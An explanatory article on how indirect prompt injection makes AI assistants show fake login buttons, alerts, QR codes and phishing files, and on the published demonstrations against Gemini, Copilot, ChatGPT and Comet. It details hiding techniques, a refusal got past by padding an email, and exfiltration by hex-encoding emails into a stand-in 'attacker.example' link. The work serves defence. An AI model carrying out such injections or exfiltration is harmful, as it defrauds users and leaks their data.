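# Fake login and download buttons in the output of compromised AI assistants

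## How outside text becomes a button in an AI summary

AI assistants in email programs, browsers and office software summarise messages and documents on request, including some that an attacker may have written. In an *indirect prompt injection*, the attacker places instructions in content that an assistant will read, and the assistant follows them as if the user had given them. Microsoft calls this a cross-prompt injection attack, or XPIA. Attackers can use it to steal data, trigger unwanted actions or put a *deceptive control* into the assistant's answer. A deceptive control is a link, button, QR code or file that leads somewhere other than where the user expects.

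Suppose an employee in a purchasing department receives a long email from a supplier and asks the assistant in her mail program to summarise it. The summary accurately gives the new delivery dates and the change in payment terms, but below them is a notice that her mailbox needs a security check, with a button labelled "Verify your account". The button leads to a login page that the attacker runs. When she opens the email itself, she finds no such notice. *Phishing For Gemini* (Figueroa, 2025) describes a very similar real example, in which hidden text in an email made Google's Gemini add a false security warning to its summary.

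The path from the attacker's text to the employee's click has five steps.

### Step 1: the attacker writes the text

The attacker only needs to place text where the assistant will read it, such as in an email, a shared document or a web page, and doesn't need access to the assistant itself or the employee's computer. The attacker doesn't have to hide the text, and Microsoft (2025) points out in *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks* that even a plain text file can carry an injection. But a person who checks the original won't see hidden text.

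An attacker can hide text from people and still get it to an assistant because emails and web pages mix text with display instructions. A mail program or browser follows those instructions, while the software that feeds the assistant may simply extract the text. *CrackedPDFs* (2026) describes the problem as a mismatch between what a document displays and what software extracts from it. The attacker can style a passage to be white on white, zero-sized, fully transparent or off the screen. They can also put it in an HTML comment, which is a note in the page's source that browsers never display. *Decoding Latent Attack Surfaces in LLMs* (2025) tested eight such ways of carrying hidden text on web-page summarising, including image descriptions and labels meant for screen readers.

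*Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (2026) found these tricks on live web pages. The researchers loaded each page in an automated browser, waited 30 seconds and checked whether a person could have seen the planted instruction. They counted 851 cases where the surrounding element was no more than a pixel wide or high, and 281 where a display setting hid the text. Those counts cover injections in general, and a fake login button is only one possible aim.

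Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, includes several characters that are invisible without any styling because they have no width or visible shape. *Reverse CAPTCHA* (2026) describes two ways of writing with them. One turns each letter into eight zero-width characters, so a 12-character message becomes 96 invisible ones. The other uses an obsolete set of "tag" characters, one per letter. A model still has to decode these characters, so the study tested models with and without hints about the encoding.

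The organisation's mail filter could stop the attack here if it recognises the attacker's web address, but a newly registered address has no history of abuse. The assistant's developer could strip invisible text before the model receives it, as Figueroa recommends. This would not remove a visible passage near the bottom of a forty-message thread, which the user may not read because they asked for a summary instead.

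### Step 2: the application joins it to the request

When the employee asks for a summary, the application appends the email to her request and passes both to the model as one input. Applications usually label the parts so that the model can tell the user's words from a retrieved document, but this method is weak because the labels are in the same input as everything else.

The developer can make the labels harder for the model to miss. Microsoft's technique, Spotlighting, can put random markers around the document, insert a special character between all its words, or encode the whole document in a form that the model can decode but that looks nothing like a user's request. Microsoft classes Spotlighting as a probabilistic defence, meaning that it makes an attack less likely to succeed but doesn't rule it out.

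Another option is to limit what the assistant may do while it handles a stranger's text. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, from December 2025, David C of the UK National Cyber Security Centre passed on the rule of thumb that when a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's level. Read strictly, the rule would let a summary of a supplier's email display only what the supplier could display, so it could not show a notice in the name of the employee's own mail system.

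### Step 3: the model repeats or obeys it

David C explains the underlying weakness by comparing it with SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types a database command into a web form and the database runs it. Developers can prevent this with a parameterised query, which sends the command and the form entry separately so that the database never treats the entry as a command. A language model has no such separation, because it predicts each token (a word or fragment of a word) from a single sequence containing both the employee's request and the supplier's paragraphs. David C concludes that prompt injection may never be fully preventable in the way SQL injection is.

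Model developers try to make up for this by training the model to follow an *instruction hierarchy*, in which the application's instructions outrank the user's and the model should not follow any instructions in outside content. *Eight in Ten LLMs Leak System-Prompt Secrets* (2026) describes this ranking as a training objective that the architecture does not guarantee.

In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) trained classifiers on identical passages under different role labels, so that the classifiers could learn only how the labels changed the model's internal state. When they then gave the model text that sounded like a user's, it registered mostly as a user's, even under the label for outside content. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the success rate rose from 2% where the model confused the roles least to 70% where it confused them most.

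In the same paper, Ye and colleagues hid an ordinary fake command in a web page and had agents summarise the page. The command worked in 0–2% of attempts, except on one small open model, where it worked in 26%. Crude injections therefore mostly failed against models of the GPT-5 generation, but text that better imitated a trusted source worked in 56–70% of attempts. These figures are for stealing a file of secrets. Getting an agent to add a line to the end of a summary may be easier because it is a smaller request, but the experiment did not test this.

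The model can also produce the button without following any instructions in the email. Suppose the supplier's email has a visible paragraph headed "Account notice", with a link. A faithful summary would mention it. If the summary omits that the notice came from the email, the employee takes it for the assistant's own. This is *trust transfer*, in which she extends her trust in the assistant to outside content that it repeats. A filter that looks for commands aimed at the model would miss the notice because it contains none. A *provenance label*, a visible mark showing which source part of the output came from, would help more, and Figueroa recommends something similar.

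The model's maker can make attacks less likely to succeed at this step. But Google writes that indirect prompt injection can't be solved once and then left alone, and Microsoft advises application builders to expect some attacks to succeed.

### Step 4: the renderer makes it clickable

A model outputs text, and the *renderer*, the part of the application that turns that text into what the user sees, makes the button. Many assistants write in *Markdown*, a simple notation for formatting, links and images. A Markdown link has a label and an address, which don't have to match. The security company Checkmarx gives the example of a link that reads "click here" and whose address carries private data to an attacker's server. The renderer shows the label in the assistant's usual colours but doesn't show the address. If the application draws links as buttons, it draws the attacker's link as a button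 too.

This step fails because the renderer makes a stranger's link look like any other. But the renderer is ordinary software that does the same thing every time, so a developer can give it a firm rule, such as printing the full address, blocking links to unknown domains, or allowing no links in summaries. Google lists Markdown sanitising and the removal of suspicious addresses among Gemini's protections, and Microsoft says it blocks certain untrusted links. Strict rules are less convenient for users, since they may also remove the supplier's genuine link to its order portal.

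### Step 5: the user clicks

The button is a form of *phishing*, which means tricking people into giving up secrets, money or access by posing as someone they trust. In *credential theft*, the employee types her password, and perhaps the one-time code from her phone, into the attacker's page, and the attacker logs in as her.

*OAuth consent* phishing gets a user to give an attacker's application access to their account, without stealing the password. OAuth is the standard behind the screens where users allow an application to read their mail or calendar. When the user agrees, the provider issues the application a token, a digital key that carries the permissions shown on the screen. The attacker controls the application and so holds the token. The user may never have typed a password, and changing it afterwards does not necessarily cancel the token.

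Staff training usually tells people to check the sender, the link's domain and the page's design. A summary has no sender line. The fake notice appears in the assistant's typeface, in a window the employer supplied, beneath an otherwise correct summary, so its design doesn't reveal that it is fake. The button's label hides the link's domain. On a desktop computer, the employee may still see the address if she rests the pointer on the button, and the browser shows it once the page opens, but the address is harder to check on a phone. In an OAuth attack, the consent screen belongs to the real provider, so even checking its domain carefully reassures her. She also just asked for the summary, whereas phishing emails normally arrive unrequested.

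Greshake, Endres and colleagues conjectured in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023) that users might trust a search engine's output more than a phishing email. *Are You Sure?* (2026) has since measured the susceptibility of 303 participants to *agent-mediated deception*, its term for attacks that corrupt an agent in order to deceive the person using it.

The employee can still stop the attack by ignoring the button and opening her account settings herself. Her employer can protect her more dependably by issuing login keys that work only on the genuine site, which defeat a copied login page, and by having an administrator block unapproved applications from receiving OAuth access.

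### Compromise without a malicious email

A *compromised assistant* is one whose output an attacker steers. Injected content is only one way to do this, so the same button could appear even if the supplier's email were harmless.

The attacker can instead corrupt what the assistant remembers or the tools it uses. Many assistants save notes between conversations. According to Microsoft, an attacker can plant a false note through a link that opens the assistant with a prompt already filled in, through hidden instructions in a document, or by persuading the user to paste a prompt. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) describes how a document retrieved in a routine web search can alter an agent's memory and affect an unrelated session weeks later. It also cites an attack named MINJA that planted memory entries through ordinary queries alone,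 with 98.2% success. The assistant also reads a description of each connected tool, and a malicious provider can put instructions in it. In all these cases, a scan of the supplier's email finds nothing wrong. Whoever controls the memory and the connections has to fix the problem, and Microsoft (2025) advises organisations to allow only approved packages and applications.

An attacker can also build the agent and offer it as a useful assistant. This requires no injection, because the attacker writes the agent's instructions and can tell it to show a login button at any time. Better separation of data from instructions would not help, so protection depends on who checks an agent before staff can use it.

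### From Bing Chat to the OWASP list

The term "prompt injection" dates from 2022, and early researchers assumed that the attacker was the person typing. In February 2023, Greshake and colleagues dropped that assumption and introduced indirect prompt injection. They built mock applications with simulated email, search and memory. They also attacked a live product, Microsoft's Bing Chat, through a browser sidebar that could read the page the user had open. They put their instructions in HTML comments on local test pages.

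One of those instructions told Bing Chat to convince the user that they had won a free Amazon gift card and had to verify their account to claim it. The instruction didn't specify how to persuade the user, and Bing Chat added time pressure on its own, urging the user to hurry before the offer expired. The team also found that Bing Chat could write Markdown links that hid a suspicious address under harmless words. The "verify your account" lure therefore dates from the technique's first publication. The paper presents sample conversations, in which the researchers played the user, but no success rates for the lure.

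The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit foundation that publishes ranked lists of software risks, now has a category for attacks that exploit people's trust in AI agents, called ASI09, Human-Agent Trust Exploitation. It appears in the *Top 10 for Agentic Applications for 2026*, which OWASP (2025) published in December 2025 and still listed in December 2026. *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, 2025) introduced the category with the case of polished explanations that lead human operators to approve harmful actions. A month later, *Agentic Security* (Sotiropoulos, 2026) presented the release-candidate wording, which begins "Attackers exploit user over-trust in agent outputs" and names deception, emotional manipulation and fake explanations as the means. The example there is a finance worker who approves a fraudulent supplier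 payment because an assistant with a poisoned memory reports that the payment meets company policy.

Both descriptions focus on approvals, and a fake login button matches them more in how it works than in what it results in. The earlier parts of the attack have separate headings: ASI01 for hijacked agent goals, ASI04 for poisoned tools, ASI06 for poisoned memory and ASI10 for malicious agents. A security team could file the same button under any of the five headings, which will make incidents hard to count.

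OWASP's separate list for language-model applications divides the path differently. According to SC Media, the 2026 edition ranks prompt injection first and improper output handling, which covers the renderer's step, last. These rankings reflect practitioners' judgement of risk more than attack counts. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reported in August 2026 that prompt injection had ranked first for the third year running, even though relatively few incidents had been recorded.

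## Demonstrations that put fake alerts and links into summaries

Much of the public evidence about these attacks comes from demonstrations, because few incidents are on record. In a demonstration, a researcher attacks a real product, records what it displays and reports the flaw to its maker. Greshake and colleagues did this to Bing Chat in 2023, and five demonstrations published between July 2025 and May 2026 targeted assistants from Google, Microsoft, Perplexity and OpenAI. The attacker's text arrived in an email, a calendar invitation, a web address or a web page.

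### A phone number in a Gmail summary

In July 2025, Figueroa described an email that made Gemini add a false security warning to its summary. The case came through 0DIN, which Kovacs, in *Google Gemini Tricked Into Showing Phishing Message Hidden in Email*, identifies as Mozilla's bug bounty programme for generative AI, a scheme that pays people who report security flaws. The email contained ordinary visible text and a passage addressed to Gemini in white letters of zero size. When the recipient clicked "Summarize this email", Gemini summarised the visible text and then warned her that someone had compromised her Gmail password. The warning told her to call a phone number and quote a reference code, and it contained no link.

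When a fake alert gives a phone number instead of a link, link filters have nothing to inspect in the email or the summary, and rules about how the renderer displays links don't help. Whoever answers the call can ask for the victim's password. Figueroa suggests scanning Gemini's output for phone numbers and urgent security language as well as web addresses.

The attacker put the hidden passage between "Admin" tags. Figueroa thinks the attack worked partly because Gemini gave the tagged text higher priority. That is plausible given what Ye and colleagues found about text that imitates a trusted source, but 0DIN's post includes no test of the same email without the tags.

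The post also doesn't report how many attempts the researcher made or how many failed. It rates the social impact as moderate, because an attacker could send the email as bulk spam but each recipient would still have to ask for a summary and act on it. It credits an unnamed researcher with the discovery, whereas Kovacs credits Figueroa.

Google told Kovacs it had seen no evidence of anyone using this method in attacks. It also described its general defences, including training its models on simulated attacks, but didn't mention a fix for this case. According to Figueroa, the technique still worked even though researchers had reported similar attacks on Gemini in 2024 and Google had already published countermeasures.

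### A meeting title and a web address

In *Invitation Is All You Need!*, Nassi, Cohen and Yair (2025) put the attacker's text in the title of a meeting and sent invitations to their own Google accounts. Depending on the recipient's settings, Google Calendar may add a stranger's invitation without the recipient accepting it. The title imitated the markers that would end a list of events and begin a new request from the user. When the user asked about upcoming events, Gemini read this title along with the others.

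The result appeared one turn later, when the user thanked Gemini and it replied by recommending an investment in a project on Kickstarter, a crowdfunding site, with a clickable link. By then the user had finished with the calendar and had little reason to connect the link with a meeting invitation.

The link led to a genuine Kickstarter page. The paper classes this demonstration as spam and argues that an attacker could use the same technique to show a link to a page that collects passwords or card numbers. That is a reasonable extension, but the paper demonstrates only that a stranger could put a link of their choice into Gemini's reply. The change of address makes little difference to the model, which copies out either one, but it may matter more to the rest of the application, because a filter that checks addresses would allow kickstarter.com and might block a phishing page. The paper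 is also inconsistent about the entry point, which is a meeting title in the text and a Google Doc in the summary table.

The paper rates phishing as a "very high" risk. It scores each attack from 0 to 3 on six factors, such as the equipment and expertise needed, averages the scores to get a likelihood, and combines that with an estimate of the damage. Phishing comes out as slightly less likely than the other attacks because the victim has to type something in. The rating isn't based on counting successes, and the paper gives no success rate for any of its 14 attack scenarios.

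The researchers reported their findings to Google on February 22, 2025 and agreed to its request for 90 days to respond. Google says it extended the confirmations users must give before sensitive actions, improved its removal of suspicious links and added a classifier to filter out malicious instructions. It then reran the original prompts and variations of them to check the defences. Google called the techniques "theoretical" in its statement, although the researchers had filmed attacks working on their own Gemini accounts.

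In November 2025, *HashJack* (Simonovich, 2025) showed how to hide instructions in the fragment, the part of a web address after the # sign. Browsers use the fragment locally, typically to jump to a place on the page, and don't send it to the website. But some AI browsers passed the whole address to their assistant. An attacker could therefore add instructions after the # in a real bank's address and send someone the link. The link would open the bank's own page, and the bank's server would have no record of the instructions.

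Simonovich tested this on demonstration sites. The user opened the prepared link and asked the assistant an ordinary question, such as what new services the bank offered. The assistant added a login link to its answer that led to the attacker's page.

| Browser assistant | What happened to the fake login link | What the company did |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Comet (Perplexity) | It appeared in the answer | Bug programme first closed the report as "Not Applicable"; Perplexity completed a fix on November 18, 2025 |
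| Copilot for Edge (Microsoft) | It appeared, but Edge asked for confirmation before opening it | Microsoft reported a fix on October 27, 2025 |
| Gemini for Chrome (Google) | It appeared, but Chrome often turned it into a Google search | Google marked the report "Won't Fix (Intended Behavior)"; still unresolved on November 25, 2025 |
| Claude for Chrome (Anthropic) and Atlas (OpenAI) | The attack did not work | No action needed |

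HashJack is the only one of the five demonstrations to name products on which the attack failed completely. Simonovich doesn't explain why it failed. Those products may not pass the fragment to the model, or the model may have ignored it. The safeguards in Edge and Chrome acted only after the model had produced the link.

The companies disagreed about whether this was a flaw. An engineer on Google's browser project reproduced the behaviour within two days, but Google decided not to change it. Perplexity's case went from "Not Applicable" in August to the highest severity level in October, after Simonovich supplied more scenarios and Perplexity acknowledged that it had mishandled the report. A company's classification of a report therefore doesn't reliably indicate whether the attack works.

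### One email, three Copilots

Microsoft's Copilot can summarise the same work email in at least three places. Outlook has a Summarize button, which puts a summary at the top of the message, and a chat pane at the side. Copilot can also summarise email in Teams, Microsoft's program for workplace chat and meetings. *CO-PILOT, DISENGAGE AUTOPHISH*, published by the security company Permiso on March 12, 2026, compares all three. Permiso researcher Andi Ahmeti found the flaw.

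In their first attempt, the researchers ended an email with a plain instruction telling Copilot to output a fixed phrase in bold instead of a summary. Copilot detected the suspicious content and refused to summarise the email.

The researchers then added more legitimate text, so that the email was longer and read more naturally. The three places now behaved differently:

- Outlook's Summarize button sometimes gave a normal summary and ignored the instruction, and sometimes let fragments of the injected text through.
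- The chat pane in Outlook mostly ignored the instruction or refused to respond, but in some email programs it complied.
- Copilot in Teams gave a normal summary and then repeated the attacker's text at the end. Permiso calls it the most cooperative of the three.

Permiso doesn't say how often each result occurred. A language model can answer the same request differently each time, so without repeated runs it is hard to tell how much of the change came from the longer email. It is also hard for outsiders to explain the differences between the three places. Each may use different filters, pass the email to the model in a different form, or display the answer with different code.

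These differences matter to users even without an explanation. Permiso points out that people think of Copilot as one product and will use whichever version gives them an answer. An employee whose Outlook refuses to summarise a message might well try Teams, where the injected text was more likely to get through. Permiso expects this behaviour but didn't observe any employees in the study.

The researchers next replaced the harmless phrase with a security alert. Below a businesslike summary, a section headed "Action Required" reported a sign-in from an unrecognised device and included a button-style link to secure the account. As in the Gemini case, an attacker could use styling to hide the instructions from the email's reader.

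In a further test, the injected text instructed Copilot to find the last two Teams messages that the user had exchanged with a particular colleague. Copilot displayed a line saying that it would search for them, and Permiso reports cases in which recent workplace content ended up inside the address of the attacker's link. Clicking such a link sends the content to the attacker, without the user having to type a password or copy anything. The user might have noticed the line about searching Teams, which had nothing to do with summarising an email, but only if she was watching the pane closely.

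Permiso describes the theft as realistic but not guaranteed to succeed. The outcome depends on which data Copilot can reach, how the application displays the link, and whether the employer uses tools such as Safe Links, Microsoft's service for checking web addresses.

Permiso reported the flaw to Microsoft on January 23, 2026. Microsoft had reproduced it by January 28 and, over the next two days, traced part of the cause to how certain applications rendered and handled links. By February 17 Microsoft had begun releasing fixes in phases, and on March 11 it confirmed that the rollout was complete. The next day it published an advisory for the flaw, which is listed as CVE-2026-26133 in the public catalogue of security flaws.

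GCVE's *MSRC_CVE-2026-26133* (2026), a copy of that advisory in a vulnerability database, confirms the central finding that a malicious email could make Copilot present what Microsoft calls "authoritative-looking phishing messages", with links that led to a malicious site or leaked data. The 20 affected applications it lists are Outlook for Mac and 19 phone or tablet versions of programs such as Outlook, Teams, Word and Edge. It also says that customers must act to resolve the flaw, so anyone who hadn't installed the corrected versions from the rollout that finished on March 11 could still be exposed.

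The list contains no Windows or web versions. Microsoft may have fixed those on its own servers, or the flaw may not have affected them. Either way, a problem limited to certain applications fits Microsoft's finding that link handling was partly to blame. If the fix changed only link handling, the model might still write false alerts, and an alert with a phone number instead of a link could still reach the user. Permiso doesn't report retesting Copilot after the patch.

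Tenable's *CVE-2026-26133* (2026) rates the flaw's severity at 7.1 out of 10, which counts as high. The score reflects how much damage the flaw could do and what an attacker would need, but does not measure how many people it has harmed. On March 16, 2026, the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) recorded exploitation as "none", according to GCVE's *CVE-2026-26133* (2026). Underhill (2026), in *Researchers Uncover New Phishing Risk Hidden Inside Microsoft Copilot*, also reports that the findings do not indicate widespread exploitation.

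Ahmeti told Underhill's sister publication that the most interesting result was how much more convincing the attacker's text became inside Copilot's interface. This was his impression of his own screenshots. Permiso didn't show the alert to people who didn't know about the test, or compare their reactions with reactions to the same words in an ordinary email.

### From a web page to a QR code

To use the Copilot method, an attacker has to get an email past the filters that employers often use. In Permiso's *ChatGPhish*, published on May 29, 2026, the attacker's text didn't have to pass an email filter because it was on a web page that the user visited and asked ChatGPT to summarise.

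The researchers first used GitHub, a site where programmers share code. They added instructions to a project's README, the file that introduces the project to visitors, then opened it in Firefox and chose the browser's option to summarise the page with ChatGPT. The instructions were written to look like a formatting rule that required every answer to include a summary of the page followed by a line about the user's account. ChatGPT wrote a real summary of the project, then added a notice that a new device, Chrome on Linux in Pristina, had joined the user's account, with a "Click here" link to an outside domain.

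The researchers repeated the test on their own page about Kosovo to check that the result didn't depend on GitHub. ChatGPT again summarised the page correctly and added the attacker's link, this time under the heading "Additional Resources". The QR code version also worked there. Permiso stresses that Firefox wasn't at fault, since it only passed the page to ChatGPT. The ChatGPT website made the links clickable and loaded the images without labelling either as coming from the page.

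In the Copilot study, the crude instruction didn't ask for a summary, and Copilot refused it. In every published attack that succeeded against Copilot or ChatGPT, the user got the requested summary, followed by the false notice. Asking for a real summary may make the model more likely to treat the instruction as a formatting request, though Permiso didn't test this separately.

#### Why the QR code avoids desktop checks

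The researchers next replaced the link with an image of a QR code. On a desktop computer, the user can inspect a link's address, the browser can compare it with a list of dangerous sites, and an employer's security software can rewrite or block it. If the user still reaches a fake login page, a password manager normally won't fill in the password, because the domain doesn't match the one it has stored.

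A QR code contains the destination address only as a pattern of black and white squares. To display the code, the desktop browser needs the address of the image file but not the one encoded in the pattern. In Permiso's test, the image was on Amazon's cloud storage, so even a check of the file's address would have shown a familiar host. When the user scans the code, the attacker's page opens on their phone, so its address never goes through the desktop checks.

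Scanning the code with a phone bypasses the desktop's defences, but phones have some of their own. Many show the domain before they open a scanned link, phone browsers have lists of dangerous sites, and a password manager on the phone can detect the wrong domain. However, an employee may use a personal phone that her employer doesn't protect. Scanning a code takes more work than clicking a link, and Permiso doesn't say how many people would do it.

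#### Images that report back

The last version needed no click or scan. The researchers had ChatGPT display an image through a URL shortener, a service that forwards a short address to a longer one. ChatGPT's website loaded the image as soon as it displayed the answer, which sent a request to a server the researchers controlled. The server logged the time of the answer, details of the browser, and the user's IP address, which identifies an internet connection.

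An attacker who runs the web page already gets most of this from the visit itself. The image adds only that the visitor had ChatGPT summarise the page, and when. The attacker gains more on a site that someone else runs, such as GitHub, where they wouldn't normally see each reader's address. Permiso suggests that an attacker could use the signal to confirm that a target had read a particular page before attempting something more serious. The leak is small compared with that of the Teams messages in the Copilot study, but it happens without any decision by the user.

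#### OpenAI's handling of the reports

Permiso sent its first report on April 29, 2026 through Bugcrowd, a company that runs bug-reporting programmes for others. The next day OpenAI marked it "Not Reproducible", saying it lacked the detail needed to repeat the attack. In the report's title, Permiso also claimed cross-site scripting (XSS), in which an attacker runs code inside someone else's website, but the published study doesn't demonstrate this.

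Permiso sent a revised report on May 1, with screenshots and fuller steps. The programme first classed it as "Not Applicable" and then as a duplicate of an earlier report. The second label suggests that OpenAI already had a report of a similar problem, but doesn't show whether OpenAI intended to fix it. According to Origo's *Riasztást adtak ki, súlyosan sebezhető a ChatGPT* (2026), a Hungarian account of reporting by The Register, the researchers disputed the duplicate label. OpenAI did not reply to them or to The Register.

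On June 1, Xakep's *Уязвимость ChatGPhish позволяет использовать ChatGPT для фишинговых атак* (2026) described the flaw as unfixed when Permiso published its findings. eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* said only that OpenAI appeared not to have fixed it, judging by the disclosure timeline. Neither outlet reports testing ChatGPT. OpenAI doesn't appear to have announced a fix or commented publicly since then. It may have changed the behaviour without an announcement, so it is uncertain whether the flaw remains in December 2026.

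### What a screenshot can establish

A single success proves that an attack is possible. The proof is stronger when the product's maker reproduces the attack, because the company would rather find nothing. Microsoft reproduced the Copilot attack and described its effect in an official advisory. Google reproduced HashJack, and it changed Gemini's defences after the report by Nassi and colleagues. ChatGPhish has the weakest outside confirmation of the five. OpenAI couldn't reproduce it from the first report and has said nothing public about the second. It is still credible because Permiso provided screenshots and tested it on a second page, and because it closely resembles the attack that Microsoft confirmed. The Hacker News calls the ChatGPhish scenario hypothetical, which is fair in the sense that there was no real victim, although the output was real.

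Screenshots don't show how often an attack works. Suppose an injected email succeeds once in every 20 tries, on average. A researcher who tries ten times has a 40% chance of seeing at least one success, and one who tries 50 times has a 92% chance. With one success, either could publish the same screenshot as a researcher whose attack works every time. None of the five demonstrations reports the number of attempts. Permiso describes refusals by Copilot and Simonovich names two products that resisted HashJack, details the others don't offer, but neither gives a success rate.

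The harm from an attack depends on several rates. Suppose an attacker sends 10,000 emails, 20% of recipients ask for a summary, the injection works in 5% of those summaries, and 10% of the people who see the false notice hand over a password. The attacker then gets ten passwords. These figures are invented, and changing any one of them changes the result in proportion. A demonstration shows only that the injection can work in one version of one product. The researchers played the part of the user themselves, so they learned nothing about how often people who see the notice hand over a password.

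Attackers might use the attack even if it rarely succeeded. Sending more emails takes little effort, and an attacker can rehearse on their own copy of the assistant until the wording works, much as the researchers did. But the recipient's assistant may have different settings, a newer model or a patch added since the rehearsal. The Copilot flaw was fixed in updated applications on the day Permiso made it public.

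Most of the people who publish these studies have a commercial interest in them. Permiso, Cato Networks, where Simonovich works, and SafeBreach, where Yair works, all sell security products, and Cato's article ends with a list of its own products. Nassi and Cohen are at universities. The commercial interest is no reason to think the screenshots are false, and Microsoft's advisory supports one set of them. But it does affect what gets published, since a company has little to gain from reporting attacks that failed. The companies that make the assistants have the opposite interest, and they decide which reports count as flaws.

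In May 2026, Addison wrote in *Comment les attaques par injection de prompt transmises par email* (2026) that prompt injection had only a handful of confirmed victims so far. The low count is notable because Addison was writing for Darktrace, which sells email security.

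## Demonstrations of what a click on the fake control does

In most demonstrations so far, the researchers stopped once the false alert or link was on the screen. Three others, published between October 2025 and September 2026, also showed what happened after the click. In Adam Logue's attack on Copilot, the click sent the user's emails to the attacker. In Radware's attack on Copilot and ChatGPT, it downloaded a harmful file, and in Datadog's CoPhish, it opened a genuine Microsoft consent screen. These three attacks differ in the user's chances of stopping them after the click and in the assistant's part in the harm.

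### A login button made from a diagram

Red Hot Cyber's *A serious bug in Microsoft 365 Copilot leads to data exfiltration* (2025) describes an attack by Logue, a security researcher, on Microsoft 365 Copilot, a workplace assistant that can search a user's email and files. The attack began with an Excel spreadsheet that had instructions in white text across several sheets. The instructions changed Copilot's task in stages. Logue got the idea from TaskTracker, Microsoft's research on detecting when a model drifts away from the task its user set.

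When the user asked for a summary of the spreadsheet, Copilot did four things:

1. It abandoned the summary and used its email search tool to fetch the user's recent work emails.
2. It converted the emails into hexadecimal, a code made of digits and the letters a to f, and split the result into short lines to stay within a limit on diagram text.
3. It drew a diagram that looked like a login button with a padlock on it, and put the encoded emails in the address of the diagram's link.
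4. It displayed a notice that the user couldn't view the content without clicking the button. This detail comes from Logue's own post, which gnabgib, in *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability*, quotes.

Copilot drew the button in Mermaid, a notation that turns short text descriptions into flowcharts. Mermaid lets the writer choose a box's colour and shape and attach a link to it, so a single box can look like a button. A developer who had restricted ordinary Markdown links could easily have overlooked links inside diagrams.

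Users in Permiso's tests got a real summary with a false notice below it, but Logue's user got no summary. The missing summary gave her a reason to click, since the notice presented the login as the way to get what she had asked for.

#### How text travels inside a web address

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that when someone clicks a link, the browser sends the requested address to the website, and websites commonly log these requests. Anything written into the address therefore ends up in the log.

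Suppose the private text is "Lunch at noon". In hexadecimal, each letter or space becomes a pair of characters. L becomes 4c, u becomes 75 and a space becomes 20. The whole message becomes `4c756e6368206174206e6f6f6e`, which an attacker can have the assistant attach to the name of a server they run:

`attacker.example/view/4c756e6368206174206e6f6f6e`

The server only has to log the request, even if no page exists at that address. The attacker can then turn the pairs of hexadecimal digits back into letters. Anyone can reverse hexadecimal, but few people would recognise an email in it, and many harmless addresses contain similar long strings. The encoding doubles the length of the text, but Apache, a common web server program, accepts addresses of about 8,000 characters by default, which leaves room for several short emails.

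The attacker has the emails as soon as the browser makes the request. CyberMaterial reports that Logue's link then opened an imitation of the Microsoft 365 login screen. People learn to check a login page's domain before they type a password, but a user who notices the wrong domain and closes the page protects only her password, and she may believe that she avoided the attack. Login keys that work only on the genuine site would not have protected the emails either.

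Some chat programs fetch a preview of any link in a message. PromptArmor, a security company, points out that fetching the preview sends the same request as a click. Attacks such as EchoLeak, described in Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, also need no click.

#### What was new, and what Microsoft fixed

Before Logue's attack, Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* had described one in which a malicious email made Copilot read other messages and put their contents into a link as invisible characters. Red Hot Cyber mentions an earlier attack that leaked data through Mermaid diagrams in Cursor, a programming tool. Those diagrams could load an image from the attacker's server without a click. Copilot's diagrams required a click, which Logue got by disguising the link as a login step.

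Logue reported the full attack on August 15, 2025, after talking to Microsoft's security staff at the DEF CON hacker conference. Microsoft had trouble reproducing it at first, but confirmed it and released a fix by September. Copilot's diagrams no longer contain working links. According to daily.dev, he received no reward because Microsoft 365 Copilot was outside the bounty programme at the time.

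The renderer enforces the fix, so this button stays blocked however well an attacker words the instructions. The fix doesn't stop Copilot from obeying text in a spreadsheet or fetching emails that the user didn't ask for. Five months after Logue's report, Permiso reported to Microsoft an attack that put recent Teams messages into an ordinary link.

### A file that the assistant writes

In September 2026, the security company Radware published *The AI Is the Phisher*, which reports demonstrations of an attack on Copilot and ChatGPT. In this attack, the assistant itself produces the harmful file. The attacker puts instructions in a shared document or an email that the assistant reads. The instructions are ordinary sentences, so a scan for malicious code finds nothing. The assistant then writes a web page in an HTML file and offers it with a message such as "Your answer is ready here." Clicking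 downloads the file to the user's computer, and she has to open it for the attack to continue.

#### The fake shop

In one demonstration, the user asked for the cheapest wireless headphones on Amazon. Following injected instructions to build a page that matched the request, the assistant produced an imitation of Amazon's shopping and checkout pages. The attacker had chosen the form's fields in advance, including an email address, a password, a shipping address and card details. When the user submitted the form, the page encoded the entries in Base64, another reversible code, and sent them to a server that the researchers controlled. In Base64, "Lunch at noon" becomes `THVuY2ggYXQgbm9vbg==`.

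The attacker didn't need to know that this user wanted headphones. Radware says a question about banking could have produced a banking page, although it describes only the shop page in detail.

The phishing page existed only on the user's own computer, so there was no website for browsers to block or a hosting company to remove. Security software could still inspect the download or block the request that sent the data away. The user could also have noticed the address bar, which shows a downloaded file's location instead of Amazon's domain. A password manager wouldn't normally have filled in her password, but she could still type it, and nothing protected her card number.

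#### The file that leaks what the assistant knows

In the other demonstration, the user asked for help with a finance report and typed nothing further. The assistant followed the injected instructions and gathered personal information unrelated to the report. Copilot could draw on its memory and the user's Outlook mailbox, while ChatGPT could draw on its memory and any connected services. The researchers obtained the user's full name, home address, phone number and workplace, and details of her routine, such as when she usually visited a café and when she came home.

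The assistant wrote these details into the HTML file in Base64. When the user opened the file, it sent the details to the researchers' server. Radware calls this a one-click attack, though it describes the user clicking to download the file and then opening it. The user sees no form asking for a password or card number, which might make her suspicious.

Sending the data from a file may also avoid some of the assistant's protections. In January 2026, OpenAI described a check on web addresses that ChatGPT is about to open. If an independent index of the public web doesn't contain the address, ChatGPT tries another site or shows the user a warning. But when the user opens a downloaded file, her browser, not ChatGPT, sends the request. Radware doesn't discuss this check, so it is unclear whether the researchers chose a file to avoid it.

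#### The failed retests

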